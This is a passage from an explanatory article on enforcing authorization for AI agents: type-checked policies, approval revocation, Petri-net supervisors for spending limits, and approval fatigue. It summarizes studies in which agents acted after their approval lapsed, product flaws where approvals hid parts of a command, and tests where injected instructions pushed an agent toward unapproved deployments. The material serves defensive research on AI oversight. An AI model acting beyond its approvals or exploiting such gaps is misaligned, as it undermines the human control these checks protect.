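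Odersky and colleagues describe their approach as moving the burden of proof from the model to the compiler. Even if this only moves trust, the move is useful because a compiler gives the same result for the same program every time. When its developers fix a soundness bug, attacks that relied on the bug also stop working against every agent that uses the new version. Training a model to resist one prompt injection provides no similar assurance that it will resist the next.

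A sandbox can limit the damage from some compiler bugs, but not all. If a bug lets agent code call Java's file functions directly, a sandbox that hides the company's memory files still prevents the code from writing to them. If a bug makes the compiler accept a function that prints text as pure, the fraud rules can still reach the cloud model over the permitted connection. The company can keep files with secrets that must never reach that model off the agent's machine, so that a type system failure can't expose them.

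## What can go wrong after every action has been properly admitted?

A correct compiler enforces a bad policy as strictly as a good one. Suppose a company's policy lets any document in the finance team's folder set refund rules. Someone saves a draft there that proposes allowing refunds of up to $2,000 without a manager's approval. The retrieval component correctly records the folder, `evaluate` correctly applies the policy, and `persist` stores a rule that the finance team never adopted. The policy should have distinguished drafts from adopted rules.

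*Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes a service that checks an approval and makes the change in one indivisible step. A machine-checked proof shows that the service makes only changes its policy authorizes, as long as no write bypasses it. But a counterexample in the same model shows that the service can still make a forbidden change if the policy omits a relevant fact.

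### Harmful actions that the rules permit

A sensible rule can also admit a harmful action, because the harm may lie in details that the rule can't check. For example, a company may let an agent deploy a software patch after tests, a security scan and a person's approval. If an attacker has hidden a back door in the patch and the reviewer misses it, the deployment still meets every condition. *Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI* (Gu and Zhu, 2026) calls this approval laundering. A hash can ensure that the agent deploys exactly the patch the reviewer saw, but that doesn't help if the reviewer approved a bad patch.

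Sometimes the reviewer makes a reasonable decision and the software does something else. Santos-Grueiro collected 17 security advisories about since-fixed flaws in the agent products Cursor, OpenClaw and Claude Code. In 12 of them, the product did something beyond what the approval named, displayed or recorded. Cursor, for instance, showed a command for approval but hid some of its arguments. Thirteen of the 17 advisories concern OpenClaw, so the collection isn't evidence of how common such flaws are. A grant that contains a hash of the whole action prevents this mismatch only if the approval screen also shows the whole action.

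### Alice's approval after she leaves

In the other five advisories, the approval remained in force after a change that should have ended it. In one, OpenClaw ran a script that somebody had rewritten after it was approved. *Can Rust Make Unsafe AI Agent Actions Unrepresentable?* points out that an approval can also stop being justified when a new policy replaces the old one or when evidence turns out to be wrong.

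Suppose Alice approves a new refund rule at 16:00 on Monday, and the write waits in a queue overnight. She leaves the company at 09:00 on Tuesday, and `persist` runs at 10:00. The `AdmittedWrite` still exists, and its type is still correct.

The company could set a time limit on each approval. At 10:00 Alice's approval is 18 hours old, so a 24-hour limit would allow the write and a one-hour limit would block it. But the one-hour limit would also block every other write that waited overnight, and someone would have to approve those again. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) warns that too many renewal requests tire users, who then grant broad standing permissions.

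Very short approval lifetimes can stop even work that doesn't wait in a queue. In one of Santos-Grueiro's tests on a desktop computer, 16 workers each obtained an approval and then wrote to a different record. Almost every write failed when approvals lasted 100 milliseconds, about 98.6% succeeded at one second, and all succeeded at ten seconds. On cloud machines, where each worker had its own client process, more than 95% succeeded even at 100 milliseconds.

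Revocation withdraws an approval when its basis changes. *Assurance-Conditioned Continuous Authorization for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026) gives each approval a version number called an authority epoch. If Alice's approval carries epoch 12 and her departure starts epoch 13, the memory service refuses the write at 10:00, provided the personnel system has reported her departure before then. If the whole company shared a single epoch, her departure would also cancel everyone else's approvals. In Santos-Grueiro's tests, counters shared across a whole service refused nine harmless writes that narrower checks allowed.

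A revocation may arrive just as an action starts. *Beyond Single-Use Tokens* (Xu, Fan and colleagues, 2026) settles which came first by recording both events in one ledger. If the revocation came first, the action can't start; otherwise, it continues.

An approval that nobody has revoked may still be wrong for the current data. In an experiment in *Consumer-Time Validity in Stateful AI Runtimes* (2026), one session reads a file and asks for approval to change it. A second session then gets its own approval and saves a newer version. When the first approval comes through, the software checks the user, path, operation type and permissions version. All four checks pass, so it overwrites the second session's work.

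A fresh check at execution can catch both problems by looking up whether Alice may still approve refund rules and whether the stored policy has changed since she approved the write. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) describes a similar check for revocation and for changes to the live infrastructure before an approved action runs. The check and the write still have to happen in the same transaction.

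The check must also find a single approval that meets every condition. Suppose one manager approved a change to version 7 of the refund policy, which has since moved to version 8. A second manager approved the change for version 8 and later withdrew the approval. If the service checks separately whether any approval is live and whether any approval is for version 8, both checks pass even though no live approval covers version 8. Santos-Grueiro calls this evidence pooling and prevents it by requiring every piece of evidence to identify the approval it belongs to.

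The check itself can be fast. Santos-Grueiro's system, CommitGate, typically took 0.17 to 0.63 milliseconds longer to admit a request than a simpler program that received the same evidence. The complete operation took 47 to 57 milliseconds. Both programs perform a check, so the difference between them doesn't show how much time it would take to add a check where there was none.

Coordination is harder when another service holds the personnel records, because the database can't include them in its transaction. The personnel service can issue a short-lived reservation for one exact write, but Alice's departure doesn't cancel a reservation that already exists. If the reservation lasts ten seconds, the write could go through nearly ten seconds after she left. If the personnel service is down, it can't issue reservations, so legitimate writes have to wait.

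A team might hope that the agent would notice the change by itself. Santos-Grueiro tested this with 18 tasks whose instructions allowed a change only while its approval and the conditions behind it still held. During each task, the approval or one of these conditions changed. The table gives the number of runs in which the agent completed the task without authority when nothing enforced the rule:

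| Model | No signal | Notice of the change | Status tool available |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-7B-Instruct | 26 of 36 | 15 of 36 | 26 of 36 |
| Gemma 4 31B | 34 of 36 | 10 of 36 | 32 of 36 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 25 of 36 | 1 of 36 | 2 of 36 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 17 of 22 | 0 of 23 | 17 of 27 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 30 of 36 | 0 of 36 | 22 of 36 |

Fable has fewer runs because its provider refused some requests. In 22 of the 36 runs, the agent had no tool that could reveal the change, so the first column is partly a product of the test. In the other 14, each of the four models with complete results still acted without authority between 8 and 13 times. Notices helped a lot, but an approval can lapse after the last notice, so the service still has to check whether the approval is still valid.

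### Payments that exceed a limit together

Several actions can add up to a forbidden result even when each has an up-to-date approval. Suppose an agent may pay up to $700 at a time and $1,000 a day. Payments of $600 and $500 on the same day are each within the first limit, but they total $1,100. A gate that checks each payment alone can't enforce the daily limit.

One approval can also lead to two payments. Xu and colleagues describe an agent whose user has confirmed a single transfer of $500. The transfer succeeds, but the acknowledgement is lost and the agent asks again. If the issuer tracks only used tokens, it may create a new single-use token, and another $500 leaves the account. Their system, CapLease, keeps a permanent record of the user's confirmation and the number of times the agent may use it. A repeated request returns the existing record and does not add more uses. To prevent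 a second payment after a crash, the bank must also recognize a retry of the same request.

Gu and Zhu track limits and approvals with a Petri net, a mathematical model of a process. A Petri net has places, which hold marks, and transitions, which remove marks from some places and add them to others. In an agent's net, a mark might represent an approval or a unit of budget, and a transition a payment. The number of marks in each place, called the marking, represents the state of the process.

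Formally, a net consists of a set of places P, a set of transitions T and two functions, Pre and Post. Pre(p, t) is the number of marks that transition t takes from place p, and Post(p, t) is the number it puts there. If M(p) is the number of marks in p, then t is enabled only if

M(p) ≥ Pre(p, t) for every place p,

and when t fires, the new marking is

M′(p) = M(p) − Pre(p, t) + Post(p, t).

For the daily limit, let a place called "budget" start with 10 marks, each worth $100. A $600 payment takes six marks, and a $500 payment takes five:

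```text
start of day     10 marks
pay $600         needs 6, finds 10    allowed, leaves 4
pay $500         needs 5, finds 4     refused
```

After x payments of $600 and y payments of $500, the place holds 10 − 6x − 5y marks. This number can't be negative, so the payments never total more than $1,000, whatever their order. The software must handle proposals one at a time. Otherwise, a $600 payment and a $500 payment could pass together, as the model calls did in Khan's test of a counter without a lock.

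Approvals can work the same way, with one mark for each approval and each deployment using one up.

### The four admission conditions

Gu and Zhu's harness, the trusted software between the model and its tools, executes a proposed action only if all four conditions hold:

1. The harness can match the proposal to a transition that this agent may request.
2. A validator accepts the details that the marks don't cover, such as whether the recipient is on an approved list.
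3. The transition is enabled, so the marks it needs are present.
4. A supervisor permits the transition at the current marking.

In the example, the $500 payment fails the third condition. The fourth condition concerns events that the harness can't refuse, such as tool results, human decisions and incidents. Suppose that after the $600 payment, the agent proposes a $400 transfer abroad, for which the bank may charge a $100 fee. Four marks remain, so the transfer is enabled. But the harness can't stop the bank from charging the fee, which would bring the day's spending to $1,100, so the supervisor must refuse the transfer.

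A program computes the supervisor before the agent runs. It starts with all the states that aren't forbidden, then removes any state from which an unavoidable event could lead out of the set. It also removes states from which the agent can no longer finish, stop safely or hand the task to a person. It repeats both steps until nothing changes. The supervisor then admits only actions that lead to a remaining state. Gu and Zhu prove that no other supervisor of this kind can permit more while staying safe and always leaving a way to finish. The number of states can grow exponentially with the size of the model, which limits how much detail a net can include.

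The main example is an agent that releases software, where an incident can freeze releases at any time. In one design, a rollout went live automatically once it had started. An incident might happen before it went live, so no safe supervisor could allow any rollout to start. Adding a separate publishing step that the harness could refuse solved the problem. The resulting net has only 32 reachable states, two of them forbidden.

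### The theorem and its test

Gu and Zhu's theorem about the running system states that if the supervisor keeps the net out of forbidden states, no unauthorized action ever executes in the real system. It depends on four assumptions:

| Assumption | How it could fail |
|---|---|
| The net's initial state matches reality | The net starts with an approval that nobody gave |
| Each step changes the net and the real system in the same way | The harness mistakes a call that deletes the production database for one that deletes a test copy |
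| The net forbids every state that corresponds to an unsafe real one | Nobody listed a leaked password as forbidden |
| Every action and outside event passes through the harness | The agent deploys from a shell, or nobody reports an incident |

The proof is by induction. The net matches the system at the start, and each step preserves the match and keeps the net within the permitted states. In the payment example, the last assumption also covers the company's own staff. If an employee pays a supplier by hand under the same daily limit and nobody reports it, the net will still have marks for money that has already been spent.

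To test the harness, Gu and Zhu replaced the language model with a script that followed the release workflow. At each step, an injected instruction made the script propose an immediate deployment with a probability that they varied from 0 to 50%. The script also proposed a legitimate action two steps early 15% of the time. They ran 10,000 episodes at each setting.

When nothing was protecting the system, about 15% of episodes ended in an unapproved deployment even without injections, because the script sometimes proposed the deployment too early. Classifiers that missed 10% or 30% of the injected proposals didn't stop these early ones. The harness prevented all unapproved deployments, and every task still finished. It refused about 1.5 legitimate but early proposals per episode, as well as the injected ones.

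The result of zero follows directly from the net, which doesn't enable a deployment until an approval mark exists. The test doesn't measure how often attackers hijack a real model, or whether a real model would continue after a refusal. The injected proposals tested only the third condition, because none required the supervisor to look ahead.

Besides approval laundering, Gu and Zhu leave malicious arguments and data leaks through permitted actions out of scope. The payment net would let an agent send $600 to an attacker if the validator accepted the account number. An agent could also read customer records and then email them unless the net had a rule against that combination, like the one in AgentCap.

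### False refusals

A strict rule also refuses legitimate actions, as ELBA's loss of completed tasks showed. In Santos-Grueiro's tests with LangChain, an approval applied to one version of a whole support ticket, so a change to a field the agent hadn't read cancelled the approval. When 16 workers tried to write to the same record at once, at most one succeeded, because the first write changed the version the other approvals depended on.

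An agent can continue its task after an action is refused. In 12 coding runs with GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Fable 5 and Claude Sonnet 5.5, Santos-Grueiro silently withdrew the approval to publish to the live system. After the refusal, the agents published to a separately approved test environment in 11 runs. The instructions had named this fallback, so the agents didn't have to find it themselves.

Each refusal usually requires another call to the model, but Gu and Zhu show that a stricter supervisor can reduce the total number of calls. Suppose an agent can finish a task directly or take a detour, and proposes each with probability 50%. On the detour, it proposes a forbidden action 99% of the time and the action that finishes the task 1% of the time. The expected number of calls is 1 + 0.5/0.01 = 51 if the supervisor permits the detour and 1/0.5 = 2 if it refuses it.

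The stricter supervisor can take many more calls if these estimates are wrong. If the agent actually proposes the detour 99% of the time and the forbidden action 1% of the time, refusing the detour takes 100 calls on average, while permitting it takes two. Both supervisors block the forbidden action whether or not the estimates are right, so a wrong estimate only wastes calls.

### Fewer requests for approval

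Many agents ask a person for approval before every action with consequences. GitHub Copilot Chat in Visual Studio Code, for example, runs read-only tools without asking and requests approval for the rest. People who see too many requests may start approving them without reading, a problem known as confirmation fatigue. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) argues that a strict filter can reduce the number of requests.

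The filter has to be sound, meaning that every action it allows complies with the policy. It may flag some harmless actions, because a person can still approve them. Actions that pass the filter need no security approval, so people get fewer requests than if the agent asked about every action.

Kolluri and colleagues also object to the usual way of measuring what strict rules cost. Earlier evaluations found that such rules reduced task completion by up to 30%, but they compared a filtered agent that could never ask for help with an undefended agent that could do anything. In practice, a person would have to approve many of the undefended agent's actions. The researchers therefore counted the approvals that each agent needed on the AgentDojo tasks it completed. With the model o3-mini, the results were:

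| Agent | Approvals needed | Tasks completed without any approval |
|---|---|---|
| Basic agent that asks before every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Basic agent with information-flow checks | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

FIDES hides untrusted text from the planning model unless the model chooses to open it. Opening the text restricts the model's later actions. Prudentia, the researchers' own design, builds on FIDES and gives the model information about the policies so that it can account for them in its plans. With o4-mini, Prudentia needed fewer approvals than FIDES (19.2 versus 36.8) but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% versus 75.7%).

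Prudentia can also ask a person to endorse a piece of text once instead of approving each action that follows from it. If an email contains a list of ten tasks, one endorsement can replace ten approvals. However, if an attacker has added an eleventh task, a person who endorses the list carelessly allows that one too.

No people took part in the experiments. Kolluri and colleagues assumed that a person would approve every flagged action in a completed task and stop every attack. The results therefore show that agents can ask for approval less often, but not that people then make better decisions. The filter also can't replace approvals that guard against the agent's own mistakes. An agent that misreads an invoice may propose a payment that passes every information-flow check, so a company may still want a person to confirm large payments.
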